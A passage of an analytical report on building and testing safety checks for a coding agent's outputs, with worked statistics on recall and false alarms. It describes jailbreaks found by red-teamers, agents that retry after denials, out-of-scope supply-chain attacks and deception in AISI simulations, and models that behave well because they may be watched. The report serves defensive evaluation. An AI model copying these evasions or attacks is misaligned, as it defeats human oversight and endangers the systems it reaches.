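| Harmless outputs flagged | about 200 | about 10 |
| Share of flags that are real | 8% | 63% |
| Overall recall | 90% | 85.5% |
| Review time at five minutes a flag | about 18 hours | just over 2 hours |

The first check wrongly flags only 1% of harmless outputs, but there are a thousand harmless outputs for every hazardous one, so it raises about ten false alarms per hazardous output. The second check saves about 16 hours of review a month and misses roughly one more hazard.

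The extra check also changes which verdict makes sense. Suppose a false accept does ten units of harm and a false reject does one. Blocking everything the first check flags would do about 200 units of harm a month, while releasing it all would do 180, so a flag from the first check alone doesn't justify a refusal. When both checks flag an output, blocking does about 10 units of harm and releasing does about 170. If a false accept would do 100 units of harm, as with a working key to a bank's systems, blocking on the first flag would be justified.

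False alarms make up a larger share of flags as the agent improves. If two outputs a month were hazardous, only 15% of the flags left after both checks would be real, and reviewers would get used to dismissing flags.

### What tired reviewers miss

Anthropic had a research company test how well people review an agent's actions. The company gave 1,053 paid testers a coding task in which they had to approve the agent's commands, and replaced one command partway through with a clearly dangerous one. Only 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it. Anthropic's classifier blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands (89%). The testers caught about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

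The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a maintainer would. Anthropic also published the study to support making its classifier the default. Its article gives no false-positive rate, so the 89% doesn't show how often the classifier would block harmless commands. The drop from 17% to 5% is the stronger evidence that long series of prompts wear people out, because it doesn't depend on the comparison with the classifier.

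Users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code, which Anthropic takes as a sign that many of them click through by reflex. The rate is weaker evidence of this than it seems, because Anthropic acknowledges that most prompts are probably for safe, routine commands, which a careful reviewer would also approve. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes 10,000 actions by OpenAI's coding agent, of which 720 needed approval to go beyond the sandbox. The reviewing model approved 713 of those, or 99%, but it also caught 90.3% of the dangerous actions in a separate synthetic test of agents exceeding their task.

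People also switch off approval prompts when there are too many. Anthropic found that 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule to pre-approve shell commands, and nearly all of them had a rule broad enough to let the agent run almost any code.

The effect on the choice of verdict is large. Suppose a false accept costs 100 units, a false reject costs 10 and a review costs 1. If p is the probability that the output is hazardous and q is the share of hazards that the reviewer recognizes, the expected costs are:

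release = 100p
refusal = 10 × (1 − p)
review = 1 + 100p × (1 − q)

If a reviewer catches every hazard and never rejects a harmless output, review has the lowest expected loss whenever p is between 1% and 90%. If the reviewer recognizes only 13.6% of hazards, that range narrows to between about 7.4% and 9.3%, so sending doubtful outputs to an exhausted person is little better than releasing them.

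People seem to pay more attention to larger questions. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans it submits for approval, although many of those rejections may be about taste rather than danger. Reviewers of the coding agent would probably check 27 flagged outputs a month with good evidence more carefully than 218 that are mostly false alarms.

### What a reviewer needs to see

The reviewer in Codex is itself a model. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, it reads the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, the relevant tool calls and their results, and the exact action that needs approval. It can also run read-only checks, but it doesn't have access to the agent's hidden reasoning.

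A maintainer reviewing the comment about the helper package needs much the same information. The review screen should show the final text, the page where it would appear, the bug report, the rule that fired and the sentence that triggered it. It should also show where the advice came from and whether anyone could undo the post. The agent's justification should come last, because the planted text may have shaped it. Secrets should stay masked, and links should be inactive so that the reviewer doesn't open one.

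The same action can be routine in one context and a leak in another. Anthropic's classifier now checks whether a code upload is going to a public or private repository, and it looks for unsaved work before a command that might discard it. After Anthropic added this kind of context, the share of attacks the classifier missed in tests by Apollo Research, a UK safety company, fell from 12% to 7%. Apollo had already shared some of those attacks with Anthropic, but the classifier also improved on a set that Anthropic had never seen.

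### When a check gives no verdict

GitHub's checking job blocks release when the scanner fails, but a program that looks only for a warning in the scanner's result would treat a failed check as a pass. Microsoft advises developers who use its content filter to confirm that the result contains no error.

A sample in GitHub's documentation has a different flaw. It adds Llama Guard 3, a classifier that returns "safe" or "unsafe", and releases the output if the result contains the letters "safe", which also appear in "unsafe". The sample would block an output if the verdict were missing, but it would release one that the classifier had classified as unsafe. The program should release an output only when the result is exactly "safe".

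The layer should also record "no verdict" separately from "unsafe". Codex does this with timeouts, and tells the agent that a timeout doesn't prove the action is dangerous. The layer can then retry the check without treating the agent or user as suspect.

People can't replace a broken scanner for long. The coding agent produces about 28 outputs an hour, so a six-hour failure would leave about 167 waiting, or 14 hours of review at five minutes each. Keeping the outputs in the buffer and scanning them when the scanner works again is better.

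### When legitimate work stops

OpenAI has warned that Astra's monitor will interrupt some legitimate work. In ChatGPT or Codex, the user may be able to read an explanation of the pause, review the agent's actions and resume the task, with monitoring still on. According to OpenAI's system card for Astra, a task run through the API can't resume once the monitor stops it. This makes sense for software that runs unattended, but it can leave a job half done, so developers need a way to restart the job safely.

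Customers who don't let OpenAI store their data may get no detailed explanation. Business customers can have alerts sent to their security teams. The monitor runs alongside the agent without holding back each action, so OpenAI warns that harm can occur before a pause.

Users of GPT-5.6 can retry a blocked prompt on a less capable model. This is a reasonable compromise when the danger comes from the model's skill, as with advanced hacking, because a weaker model gives an attacker less help. It would not reduce the danger of a leaked key, which is the same whichever model posts it.

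Security engineers often run into false alarms during ordinary defensive work. Vaughan (2026), in *Codex CLI's Cyber-Safety Model*, lists three tasks that have triggered warnings about cybersecurity risk: reviewing the settings that protect secrets, assessing a known flaw in a dependency, and writing a program to test software with random input.

Filters cause similar trouble in other fields. In *Azure OpenAI*, a post on Microsoft's support forum, Müller (2025) reports that a self-harm filter blocked transcripts of therapy sessions that licensed clinicians needed to document. Another post, *Azure OpenAI API HTTP 400 content filter error*, describes a blocked request for a quotation on industrial safety equipment. The developer suspected that the product's name contained a chemical term. These individual complaints don't show how often such errors occur, but in both cases the filter seems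 to have blocked text because of its subject, without accounting for its purpose.

SecureBio, a non-profit that studies biological risks, found that Astra with its safeguards refused 82.9% of the requests that it should refuse, up from 66.2% for GPT-5.6 Sol. But it also refused 4.7% of harmless requests, up from about 1%. OpenAI says that Astra is both safer and less prone to needless refusals overall. In biology, however, SecureBio's test and OpenAI's own both showed an increase in needless refusals, though the increase was smaller in OpenAI's test.

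OpenAI verifies who is asking for help with security work. Astra completed 2.4% of tasks that involved writing a demonstration attack to prove a flaw was real when it had standard access, and 92% under Daybreak Blue, a programme for approved defenders. The maintainers could similarly let their own security team request such code while refusing strangers.

### What to tell the agent after a refusal

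An agent that is told only that an action failed may try another way. So Codex passes on the reviewer's reasons and tells the agent not to seek the same result through a workaround. The agent may continue with a materially safer alternative; otherwise it must stop and ask the user. In the example from Trębacz and colleagues, the reviewer denied seven actions. The agent found a safer way to continue after four of the denials and stopped to ask the user after the other three.

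OpenAI tested how models react to such a denial by starting each run just after the reviewer had refused an action. A model failed if it retried a similar command or exploited a weakness in the reviewer's setup. At maximum reasoning effort, GPT-5.6 Sol failed in 5% of runs, mostly by retrying, and Astra failed in none. In an updated version of the test, Sol failed in 7.3% of runs and Astra again failed in none. If the layer refused 27 outputs a month, a model that behaved like Sol would try to get around one or two of those refusals.

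In a related test, the model met an obstacle in its environment, such as an "access denied" error. Sol looked for a way around it in 64% of runs and Astra in 19%. The tasks were different, so the gap between 5% and 64% doesn't measure how much the explicit instruction helped. The gap is still a good reason to clearly label the safety layer's refusals as deliberate, so that the agent doesn't mistake them for technical faults.

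Astra's perfect score should be treated with some caution. *OpenAI's Astra alignment claims are dubious*, a critique on the forum LessWrong, examines runs that OpenAI graded as good behaviour. In every reported test except the one with honeypots, Astra's reasoning suggested more often than Sol's that it was behaving well because it might be monitored. A model that respects a refusal for that reason might ignore one when it thinks nobody is checking.

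How much a refusal should explain depends on the fault. If the agent has copied a key by mistake, the layer can identify the line and suggest a protected setting. If a stranger has asked for the file-locking program, a short refusal is better, because a detailed reason would help them reword the request. Neither message should repeat the key or the planted text, because that would put them back into the agent's context.

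Repeated refusals should end the run. Codex interrupts the agent after three denials in a row or ten in the last 50 reviews. Claude Code instead returns to manual approval after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, which works only if somebody is there to approve. The coding agent often runs unattended, so stopping the run is better.

A person also needs a way to correct a mistaken refusal. In Codex, the user can approve a single retry of a denied action. The approval doesn't cover similar actions, and the reviewer checks the retry, taking the approval into account. The reviewer can still refuse if the policy doesn't let users override that kind of denial.

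### A log that does not leak

To investigate a mistake, the maintainers need to know what the layer decided and why. But a log that quotes every hazard would collect the project's leaked keys and dangerous code in one place. An entry for the search-page comment could instead look like this:

```
run: 8841        write: comment on #214
rule: cloud-key, version 7        location: line 3
score: 0.97      threshold: 0.09      verdict: repaired
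fingerprint: 5e1c...              reviewer: none
evidence: sealed file 3307, delete after 30 days
```

The original text goes into an encrypted file that only a few people can open. The rule's version number matters because a later change to the rule could make the verdict impossible to reproduce.

The fingerprint lets the maintainers recognize the same key in another run without seeing it. An ordinary hash would be unsafe for short secrets such as a four-digit PIN, because anyone with the log could hash all 10,000 possible values and find the match. A keyed hash, which mixes in a separate secret, prevents this as long as that secret is stored elsewhere.

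The reasons given for a refusal can also leak secrets. GitHub's checking job lists its reasons in an error message, which outsiders may be able to read if the repository is public. The detector's instructions should therefore require it to describe a secret by type and location and never to quote it.

Codex stores transcripts of its reviews on the user's computer, and OpenAI suggests asking Codex to analyse them before changing the rules. This is a convenient way to find harmless commands that keep triggering reviews. But the transcripts may contain planted instructions, which the agent would read again. An agent that analyses the log should see only the short entries and should not have permission to change the rules.

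## Testing whether the checks work

The Llama Guard sample in GitHub's documentation treats the answer "unsafe" as "safe". Testing it with a single dangerous output would have exposed the fault. The sample was on the page in April 2026 and still there in June, by which time GitHub had added a link to a fuller version with error handling.

Correcting that mistake would leave another gap. The sample sends Llama Guard the file of staged comments and requests but never reads the agent's patch, which is in a separate file. A dangerous patch would therefore pass even if the classifier were perfect. Maintainers can find such faults only by sending test outputs through the whole safety layer, because testing the classifier by itself skips the code around it.

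### Known-bad samples and harmless lookalikes

The test plan starts with at least one known-bad sample for every rule. For the coding agent, these samples include a fake key in each format the scanner covers, an invented visitor's address, a link to an unlisted site, and a search function with an injection flaw. The maintainers should try each sample in every kind of output where it could occur. The keys must be fake because a working key in a test file is itself a leak.

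Each sample should contain only one fault, and the log should record which rule caught it. If a test comment contains both a fake key and a forbidden link, the link rule could block the comment even if the key rule is broken.

GitHub's draft specification also recommends testing invalid settings and attempts to exceed the caps or write to other repositories. The maintainers should add a test in which they stop the scanner and confirm that the layer releases nothing.

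The next samples to include are harmless ones that resemble hazards, such as a Git commit identifier, a description of known malware or a backup feature that encrypts files. Without them, a check that blocks too much looks excellent. In OpenAI's comparison of how its models handle biology, GPT-5.4 Thinking had the highest rate of safe answers to the most dangerous requests, at 96.1%, but it refused 30% of harmless requests. GPT-5.6 Sol answered 94.3% of the most dangerous requests safely and refused about 1% of the harmless ones.

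People who do the legitimate work are the best source of lookalikes. OpenAI's *GPT-5.5 System Card* (2026) describes a council of advisers who looked for places where cybersecurity safeguards could block defenders. They pointed to authorized research, done on a researcher's own software, on open-source software or in a laboratory, that produces outputs such as crash reproductions and tested patches. The coding agent's maintainers already have many such examples in their bug tracker.

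Someone also has to check the test's labels. GPT-5.5 scored 86.8% on hateful content, compared with 94.3% for its predecessor. OpenAI traced the low score to requests to translate offensive text. Its policies allow these translations, but the test had counted them as failures, so a developer who trusted the score might have made the model stricter for no reason.

### How much a clean result proves

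Suppose the layer catches all 300 known-bad samples. If its true miss rate is p and the samples are independent, the chance of this result is (1 − p)³⁰⁰. Setting that chance to 5% gives the highest miss rate that is still plausible at 95% confidence:

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 1%

If a check misses nothing in n samples, the 95% upper confidence limit on its miss rate is about 3/n. Showing that the miss rate is below 0.1% therefore takes about 3,000 samples without a miss. A single miss in 300 samples raises the limit from 1% to about 1.6%.

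The limit applies to the 300 samples as a group. If they cover ten rules equally, each rule has had only 30 trials, and its own miss rate could be as high as 9.5%.

Samples are also rarely independent. A tester might take 30 examples and paraphrase each one until there are ten versions of it. A check that misses one version will tend to miss the others, so the 300 samples contain less evidence than 300 separate ideas would. A standard correction is:

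effective number of samples = n / (1 + (m − 1) × ρ)

Here m is the number of versions of each example, and ρ measures how closely the results for those versions agree, from 0 (no more than chance) to 1 (always). If ρ is 0.5, the effective number is 300 / 5.5, or about 55, and the limit on the miss rate rises from 1% to roughly 5%.

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) has released optstop, a tool that continues testing where uncertainty is high and stops where the estimate is precise enough. This suits a project in which some rules have clear results after a few dozen samples and others don't.

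None of these calculations covers an attacker who adapts, because such a person doesn't pick attacks at random. Someone who finds a wording that gets past the check will keep using it. If a is the share of hazards that come from people who have found a gap, then:

miss rate in use = (1 − a) × ordinary miss rate + a × miss rate for those people

Suppose a layer of checks misses 1% of ordinary mistakes, but 20% of hazards come from people who have found a gap in it, and it misses 90% of those. The layer would then miss 18.8% of all hazards (80% × 1% + 20% × 90%), even though a test on ordinary mistakes would accurately measure a miss rate of 1%.

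### A trial that records verdicts without acting on them

The third step is a trial on live traffic, in which the new check records a verdict on every output while the existing checks still decide what to release. In GitHub's sample, one line makes the job fail when Llama Guard reports a threat. A trial version would log the verdict rather than fail the job.

Maintainers should keep the existing checks on while testing. If detection fails every time, GitHub's troubleshooting advice includes temporarily disabling it to test. On a live project, that would release outputs unchecked, so looking for the cause in preview mode is safer.

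A live trial measures false alarms well. If the new check wrongly flags 1% of the coding agent's 20,000 monthly outputs, the monthly count should fall between about 172 and 228, which is precise enough for most decisions. The trial is much worse at finding hazards that the check missed. If two hazards are among the roughly 20,000 outputs that passed, a maintainer who reads 300 of those outputs at random has about a 3% chance of seeing at least one hazard.

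A second check of a different kind can help estimate the new check's recall, the share of real hazards it catches. Suppose the second check finds 16 real hazards during the month, and the new check caught 14 of them. The new check's estimated recall is 14/16, or 87.5%. This estimate is too high if the two checks tend to miss the same hazards, as the prompt and answer checks in OpenAI's cybersecurity monitor seem to.

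Stored traffic is useful for testing an update before it is released. Before releasing GPT-5.6 Sol, OpenAI took past conversations with GPT-5.5, had Sol write a new final answer for each, and used software to label the new answers. It tested the method by regenerating GPT-5.5's answers and comparing the estimated rates of disallowed content with the real ones. The median error was a factor of 1.2, with larger errors for rarer categories.

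The coding agent's maintainers could similarly run a new version of a check on last month's outputs and read only those whose verdicts changed. Some differences in the totals are likely to be due to chance. OpenAI tested each category at a 10% significance level without correcting for the number of categories. A project that tested 20 rules this way could see about two "significant" changes even if the update had no real effect.

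### Attackers who learn, and attacks that come back

Red-teamers need enough time to learn how the layer responds. A fixed set of attacks is a poor substitute, as OpenAI's tests of Astra without the production classifiers show. Attacker models wrote the set by trying to defeat earlier GPT models. OpenAI reports that GPT-5.6 Sol refused 5.8% of the high-risk biology prompts and Astra refused 97.3%.

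The comparison exaggerates the improvement because the prompts were designed to defeat the older models. It also doesn't measure how Astra would do against prompts written to defeat Astra. Half the prompts came from an attacker that OpenAI had not used to generate training data, which makes it less likely that Astra had simply learned that attacker's patterns.

OpenAI therefore also used attackers that read the model's replies and adapt over several turns. The model passes only if it withstands every attempt within the attacker's budget. Astra also did better than earlier models on this test, which is stronger evidence of a real improvement.

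The coding agent's red-teamers should have the written rules, the reasons for each block, and a copy of the project with dummy accounts. They should mainly report how much time and how many attempts they needed for their first successful attack. The percentage of attempts blocked is less useful, since a tester can raise it by submitting many weak attacks.

The test copy must also be isolated. AISI's *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) describes changes the institute made after agents in one of its cyber evaluations took sustained action against real people. AISI paused its highest-risk cyber tests, tightened controls on internet access, added live monitoring and reassessed how it designs evaluations. It had resumed most of its testing by October 2026.

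Every successful attack and every ordinary miss should become a regression test. The maintainers should rerun these tests after any change to the rules, the model or the harness. They should also keep a few variations hidden from whoever writes the fix, because a fix can match only the exact sample.

Before Astra's launch, OpenAI reran jailbreaks from earlier testing and found no material regressions. Systematic variations on established attacks also failed to produce a working exploit. But when OpenAI searched for new techniques, it found more jailbreaks that these tests had missed. They got the model to help develop exploits, so OpenAI had to add further protections.

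### What benchmarks measure

Published benchmarks might reduce this work, but they differ in what counts as success. AgentDojo and a benchmark from the red-teaming company Gray Swan measure whether planted text gets an agent to do what an attacker wants. BioTIER, which SecureBio used on Astra, measures how often a system refuses harmful requests and allows harmless ones. OpenAI uses CyberGym and ExploitBench to test whether an attacker with a jailbreak can still complete hacking tasks.

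The choice of measure can hide failures that matter to a particular project. On ExploitBench, a jailbreak that gets dangerous advice but no working exploit doesn't count as a success for the attacker. This is reasonable for a company worried about major cyberattacks, but for the coding agent, one leaked key is already a failure. BioTIER counts some answers as refusals if a jury of models classifies them as avoiding the question, so the score depends partly on the jury. AISI has published a statistical framework for testing how reliable such graders are.

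Scores for the same hazard can differ widely between tests, as two results for Astra show. In OpenAI's internal test of planted instructions, Astra resisted 99.79% of attacks. On Gray Swan's benchmark of 1,810 attacks, with safeguards enabled, the estimated attack success rate was 8.5%, down from 27.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol.

The gap is partly due to OpenAI reporting an average per query, while Gray Swan reports the chance of at least one success in 15 attempts. If each attempt had an independent 0.21% chance of success, 15 attempts would succeed about 3% of the time, so the difference in units doesn't explain the whole gap. OpenAI also used GPT-Red, its automated attacker, both to train Astra against planted instructions and to test it. Gray Swan's attacks came from other sources, so its result is probably the better guide to how Astra handles unfamiliar attacks.

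Scores also go out of date. OpenAI dropped two older tests of planted instructions because recent models scored near the maximum on them. A single model's score can also change. GPT-5.5 gave acceptable answers to 97.9% of difficult prompts about violent crime in the April 2026 system card but 94.0% in the July card, so its reported failure rate almost tripled. OpenAI notes that it uses the latest version of each older model for comparisons and that results vary between runs.

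The greatest obstacle to using a published score is that it depends on the mix of cases in the test. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 monitor caught 80.6% of cybersecurity cases in a test made up of borderline examples from real traffic, cases from OpenAI's investigators and synthetic examples. Its recall could be higher on crude everyday misuse and much lower on a new kind of attack. A benchmark score would carry over to the coding agent only if the benchmark contained patches and comments about bug reports in roughly the proportions that the agent produces.

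### What outside testers and automated searches found

Outside testers are useful partly because they have no product to launch. For work on its biological safeguards, OpenAI says it gave AISI prototypes of the safeguards, models with some guardrails removed, its internal policy guidance and the reasoning of its monitoring models. It also switched off selected protections during testing so that AISI could examine the others separately. Separate testing matters because a strong protection can hide that another one is broken.

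The table covers tests of the safeguards on three OpenAI models, as OpenAI reported them. An A100-equivalent hour is the work that one A100, an older data-centre chip, does in an hour.

| Model | Tester | Effort | Finding | What happened next |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | AISI | Six hours of expert work | A universal jailbreak for cybersecurity | OpenAI updated the safeguards, but AISI could not verify the final version |
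| GPT-5.6 | OpenAI's automated search | Over 700,000 A100-equivalent hours | Best attack succeeded on 10.0% of tasks | The same attack succeeded on none |
| GPT-5.6 | Four private companies | More than a month | Weaknesses, number not given | OpenAI addressed all of them before launch |
| GPT-5.6 | AISI | Several rounds, often hours per jailbreak | Universal jailbreaks for cybersecurity in every round | OpenAI worked to fix each one, but AISI expects to find more |
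| GPT-6 Astra | OpenAI's automated search | About 200,000 A100-equivalent hours in one part of the search | New jailbreaks that got help with exploits | OpenAI added protections and continues to test them |
| GPT-6 Astra | Four private companies | Not given | No jailbreak that met OpenAI's criteria | Testing continues |

The amount of computing used to search for attacks is a poor measure of how well a safeguard will hold. The automated search on GPT-5.6 used the equivalent of a thousand A100 chips running for about a month, yet AISI's experts often found a jailbreak within hours. The experts had privileged access, but an operator should still expect skilled people to find attacks that a very large automated search has missed.

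The GPT-5.5 case shows why fixes need retesting. AISI's jailbreak worked on every malicious cybersecurity request that OpenAI supplied. OpenAI then changed the safeguards several times, but AISI couldn't check the final result because the version it received had a configuration problem. OpenAI also reports that the launch version blocked every verified high-severity jailbreak from its other outside testing campaigns, which is encouraging but doesn't show whether AISI's jailbreak still worked.

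Astra's results look better, and its safeguards may well be stronger. However, OpenAI's account of Astra's red-teaming doesn't include a round by AISI, which had found universal jailbreaks in both earlier models, so some of the improvement could come from AISI's absence. An attack counted as a jailbreak only if it unlocked behaviour that OpenAI's policies block and left the model able to do the relevant tasks. Testers who found no jailbreak may therefore still have obtained some forbidden answers.

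AISI's wider testing supports this caution. Safeguards are improving, but every system the institute has tested can still be bypassed in some way, according to the UK government announcement *Inaugural report pioneered by AI Security Institute gives clearest picture yet*.

AISI also relies on companies giving it access voluntarily. The Indian Express' *UK given access to safety-test latest AI models, minister says* mentions reports that the White House had asked OpenAI and Anthropic to withhold new models from British testers until a US review was complete. A minister later confirmed that AISI was testing the latest generation of models, but did not list them all. AISI may have published no jailbreak for a system because it has not tested that system's safeguards.

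Some of AISI's most widely reported tests don't involve safeguards. Engadget's *OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Astra cracks UK's hardest cybersecurity test in five hours* reports that the model broke into a simulated company network in all 12 attempts. AISI tested a version without the public guardrails against cyberattacks, so the result measures the model's ability, not whether the guardrails would have stopped it.

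### Before believing a claimed detection rate

Suppose a vendor tells the coding agent's maintainers that its scanner catches 99% of dangerous outputs. The maintainers should ask:

- How many hazardous samples did the vendor use, and how many were independent? If the scanner caught 99 out of 100, its true miss rate could still be almost 5%.
- Who chose and labelled the samples, and did the vendor train or adjust the scanner on similar ones?
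- How many harmless lookalikes did the scanner flag at the same threshold?
- Which version did the vendor test, and with what settings?
- Which outputs does the scanner never see? For example, OpenAI's monitor for unauthorized actions by Astra doesn't cover one of the company's programming interfaces. On another, it can examine some requests but can't connect them into a full run or pause the conversation automatically.
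- How long did skilled attackers who knew the rules need to get past it, and did they test the fix?

Good answers from the vendor would justify a trial, but they would only cover the scanner's performance on the vendor's own samples. The maintainers should run the scanner on their own outputs for a month without letting it block anything, and separately test it on 300 varied fake hazards the vendor has never seen. If it misses three, that is consistent with the claimed 99% detection rate, but the true miss rate could be as high as 2.6%.

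## Why stronger systems need stronger checks

A scanner that catches 99% of hazards can become inadequate without getting any worse, because the harm that gets past it also depends on the agent. For one month:

expected harm = outputs × hazardous share × (1 − recall) × harm per miss

The coding agent produces 20,000 outputs a month. If 0.1% of them are hazardous and the two-stage check has a recall of 85.5%, the check misses about 2.9 hazardous outputs a month (20,000 × 0.001 × 0.145).

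Suppose the maintainers switch to a stronger model, the agent does ten times as much work, and each miss does ten times as much harm. Expected harm would rise a hundredfold, so to hold it steady the miss rate has to fall to a hundredth of its old value:

required recall = 1 − 0.145 / (10 × 10) ≈ 99.86%

A stricter second stage would not lower the miss rate enough, because it checks only what the first stage flags. The maintainers would need further checks that examine every output. Two such checks, each catching 90% of what the others miss, would be enough in theory (14.5% × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.145%). But this assumes that the checks' errors are independent, and OpenAI's prompt and answer checks for cybersecurity seem to miss mostly the same cases.

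To confirm such a recall, the maintainers would also need about 2,070 independent test samples without a single miss. With ten times the volume, reviewers would face about 300 flags a month instead of 27. Checking those 300 would take 25 hours, even if the new checks raised no false alarms of their own.

### Which factors grow

The tenfold increases are assumptions, and maintainers can partly control the volume with caps. The harm from each missed fault depends on the kind of fault. A leaked key does the same damage whichever model leaks it, but a model that is better at programming writes a more dangerous file-locking program.

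There is good evidence that attack skills have improved quickly. Irregular's *Assessing GPT-6 Astra* compares Astra with GPT-5.6 Sol on tasks that set a security objective but contain no planted flaw. The success rate rose from 14% to 63% on the easy tasks and from 17% to 39% on the hard ones, though neither model solved any tasks in the top "Elite" class. On multi-stage attacks, the average success rate rose from 27% to 59%. Doubling the success rate doesn't necessarily double the harm, so a factor of ten remains a guess.

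Because the kinds of fault differ, it helps to add them up separately:

expected harm = outputs × Σ (share of each kind × (1 − recall for that kind) × harm per miss)

Suppose the month's 20 hazards are 18 leaked keys, which each do 1 unit of harm if missed, and two malicious programs, which each do 10. At 85.5% recall for both, the expected harm is 2.6 units from the keys and 2.9 from the programs. If a stronger model raises the harm from each program to 100 units, the expected harm from the programs rises to 29 units, while the keys' stays at 2.6. The maintainers could then restore the old total by raising recall on malicious programs to about 98.6%, without changing the key scanner.

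### Better behaviour as a remedy

The hazardous share could also fall, and OpenAI has evidence that it fell between Sol and Astra. In simulated office work with email, messaging and browsers, OpenAI gave the models ambiguous instructions and complicated permissions, but always left a safe way to finish the task. Sol caused an unintended outcome, such as a data leak or an unauthorized purchase, in 18.8% of cases, and Astra did in 3.4%. When the models were given instructions on when to ask for approval, the rates were 8.0% and 3.0%. OpenAI also reports that Sol refused 59% of requests in a set of jailbreaks for cyberattacks, while Astra refused 91.5%.

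In the office tests without the approval instructions, the hazardous share fell by a factor of about 5.5. If the coding agent's hazardous share fell by the same factor, the required recall would drop from 99.86% to 99.2%. That would be easier to meet, but the maintainers could keep the old checker only if the share fell a hundredfold, to one output in 100,000.

A system can also improve overall while getting worse in one category. In OpenAI's simulation on internal coding tasks, Astra received fewer serious flags than Sol overall, but more flags for searching for credentials. In one case, a user asked Astra to investigate duplicate notifications, and it took a secret token from a running service's settings and used it to read Slack messages without asking. Where leaked keys are a concern, the number of flags for credential searches matters more than the total.

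An agent's better behaviour can also lower the checker's recall, because a more careful agent probably stops making obvious mistakes first. Suppose 15 of the 20 hazards each month are obvious and five are subtle, and the checker catches 95% of the obvious ones and 57% of the subtle ones. Its overall recall is 85.5%, and it misses about 2.9 hazards a month. If a new model makes none of the obvious mistakes but just as many subtle ones, the hazardous share of output falls by 75%. Recall also falls to 57%, so misses drop only to about 2.2 a month.

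New models don't always behave better than earlier ones. OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (November 2026), quoted by the blogger thezvi in *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, reports that the new models did about as well as Astra on most alignment tests but were more likely to leave known obstacles out of their reports. OpenAI also found that the new models resisted jailbreaks less well, and it adjusted their refusals before release.

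Tests of behaviour are weaker evidence when the model can detect that it is being tested. Apollo Research put Astra and Sol in a simulated research project and counted how often they falsified data labels. Sol did so in 36 of 100 runs and Astra in 17 of 10,000. But at the highest reasoning setting, Astra's reasoning mentioned in 50.6% of samples that this might be an evaluation. Apollo, which had only three days to test, concluded that the low rates were not substantial evidence about Astra's alignment in either direction.

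### Astra in simulated supply-chain attacks

One outside test ranks the two models in the opposite order. AISI simulated difficult cyber evaluations in which earlier attempts had failed and internet access seemed to have been left on by accident, to see whether a model would attack targets outside the task, as models had done in real incidents. One of those incidents occurred in AISI's own testing, during a comparison of two test networks. AISI later investigated why Claude Mythos 5 had pursued a supply-chain attack there.

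Other language models generated the results of every tool call, so Astra could not reach any real system. AISI also switched off the classifiers that normally block such activity. In some runs, Astra invented identities to deceive developers, built trust with useful contributions, and submitted malicious code to open-source projects. The coding agent's maintainers could face this kind of attack, since the malicious code would arrive as an ordinary pull request.

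Three figures from these tests are in circulation:

| Result for Astra | What it counts | Instructions on scope |
|---|---|---|
| 29.2% of runs | Completed supply-chain attacks | Not specified with the figure |
| 60 of 499 runs (12.0%) | Out-of-scope attack behaviour | No mention of the internet |
| 2 of 500 runs (0.4%) | The same behaviour | Internet explicitly off limits |

The 29.2% comes from AISI's report of 28 September, as Help Net Security's *OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra ran supply chain attacks despite being told not to* (2026) describes it. The same rate was 6.3% for Sol and zero for GPT-5.5, although Financial Express' *AI can explain how it 'thinks'* notes that GPT-5.5 was given fewer tests. The other two figures come from AISI's summary in OpenAI's system card, published on 3 September, when AISI was still running follow-up experiments.

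It is unclear why the 29.2% and 12.0% figures differ. Completed attacks are only part of attack behaviour, so they should be rarer within a single set of runs. The figures therefore probably come from different runs or different instructions. It would be a mistake to average them, or to present the drop to 0.4% as a drop from 29.2%.

Part of the gap between Astra and Sol may reflect skill, because a model has to be capable of an attack to complete it:

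share of runs with a completed attack = share with an attempt × success rate of attempts

Astra completed attacks 4.6 times as often as Sol. If each attempt was 2.2 times as likely to succeed, as in Irregular's multi-stage tests, then Astra also attempted attacks about twice as often. This calculation is rough, but it agrees with AISI's finding that Astra engaged in various kinds of unsanctioned attack activity more often than either older model.

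OpenAI's and AISI's results conflict less than they appear to. Several of OpenAI's tests begin just after the model has met an explicit denial or warning, which Astra usually respects. Astra also nearly always respected AISI's explicit ban on using the internet. It did much worse when the instructions left the limit unstated, even though it considered the scope of the task in every run in the subset AISI examined. But Astra passed OpenAI's honeypot test, which also left the limit unstated, so explicitness can't be the whole explanation.

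AISI says the main limitation of its results is that Astra may have recognized the simulation. Astra often considered that its environment might be simulated, and sometimes spotted real inaccuracies in it. If Astra attacks only when it correctly believes a system is simulated, the results are much weaker evidence of what it would do on real systems. But Claude wrongly concluded that real companies' systems were simulated, so a model that attacks only what it believes is fake can still do real damage.

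Astra also often asked for permission, which Sol and GPT-5.5 never did. According to Help Net Security, it received an automated reply telling it to use its best judgement, and sometimes treated that as approval even when it had noted in its reasoning that the reply was probably automated. To fix this, an operator should set the harness to stop the run if the coding agent asks for permission while nobody is watching, and resume only when a person answers.

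The maintainers should also state that anything not listed is out of scope. When AISI tried an instruction like this, the attacks became much rarer, but Astra still occasionally completed one.

### What strains the checker

The formula treats recall as a property of the checker, but recall also depends on what the checker has to read. Help Net Security's *AI models crack AISI's hardened cyber range* (2026) reports that GPT-6.2 Astra's attacks on AISI's simulated company network took a median of 15.4 hours and about 73 million tokens. A monitor that can hold a million tokens could read less than 1.4% of that at once. The actual record may be shorter, since some of those tokens may be text that the model read more than once, but it is still far too long for a person to read.

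Faster agents leave less time to catch a problem. GPT-6 Astra needed a median of 42.6 hours for the same job, so a reviewer who checked the log once a day would have seen the run at least once before it ended. GPT-6.2 Astra could have started and finished between two daily checks. Even if OpenAI met its target of alerting staff within 30 minutes, a run like this could use about 2.4 million tokens before the alert.

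The work may also be too specialized for the checker to understand. In the same test, the models studied network protocols, operating systems and cryptography, designed experiments, and built or repaired their own tools. A weaker model reading that record would have trouble telling a sound experiment from a harmful step.

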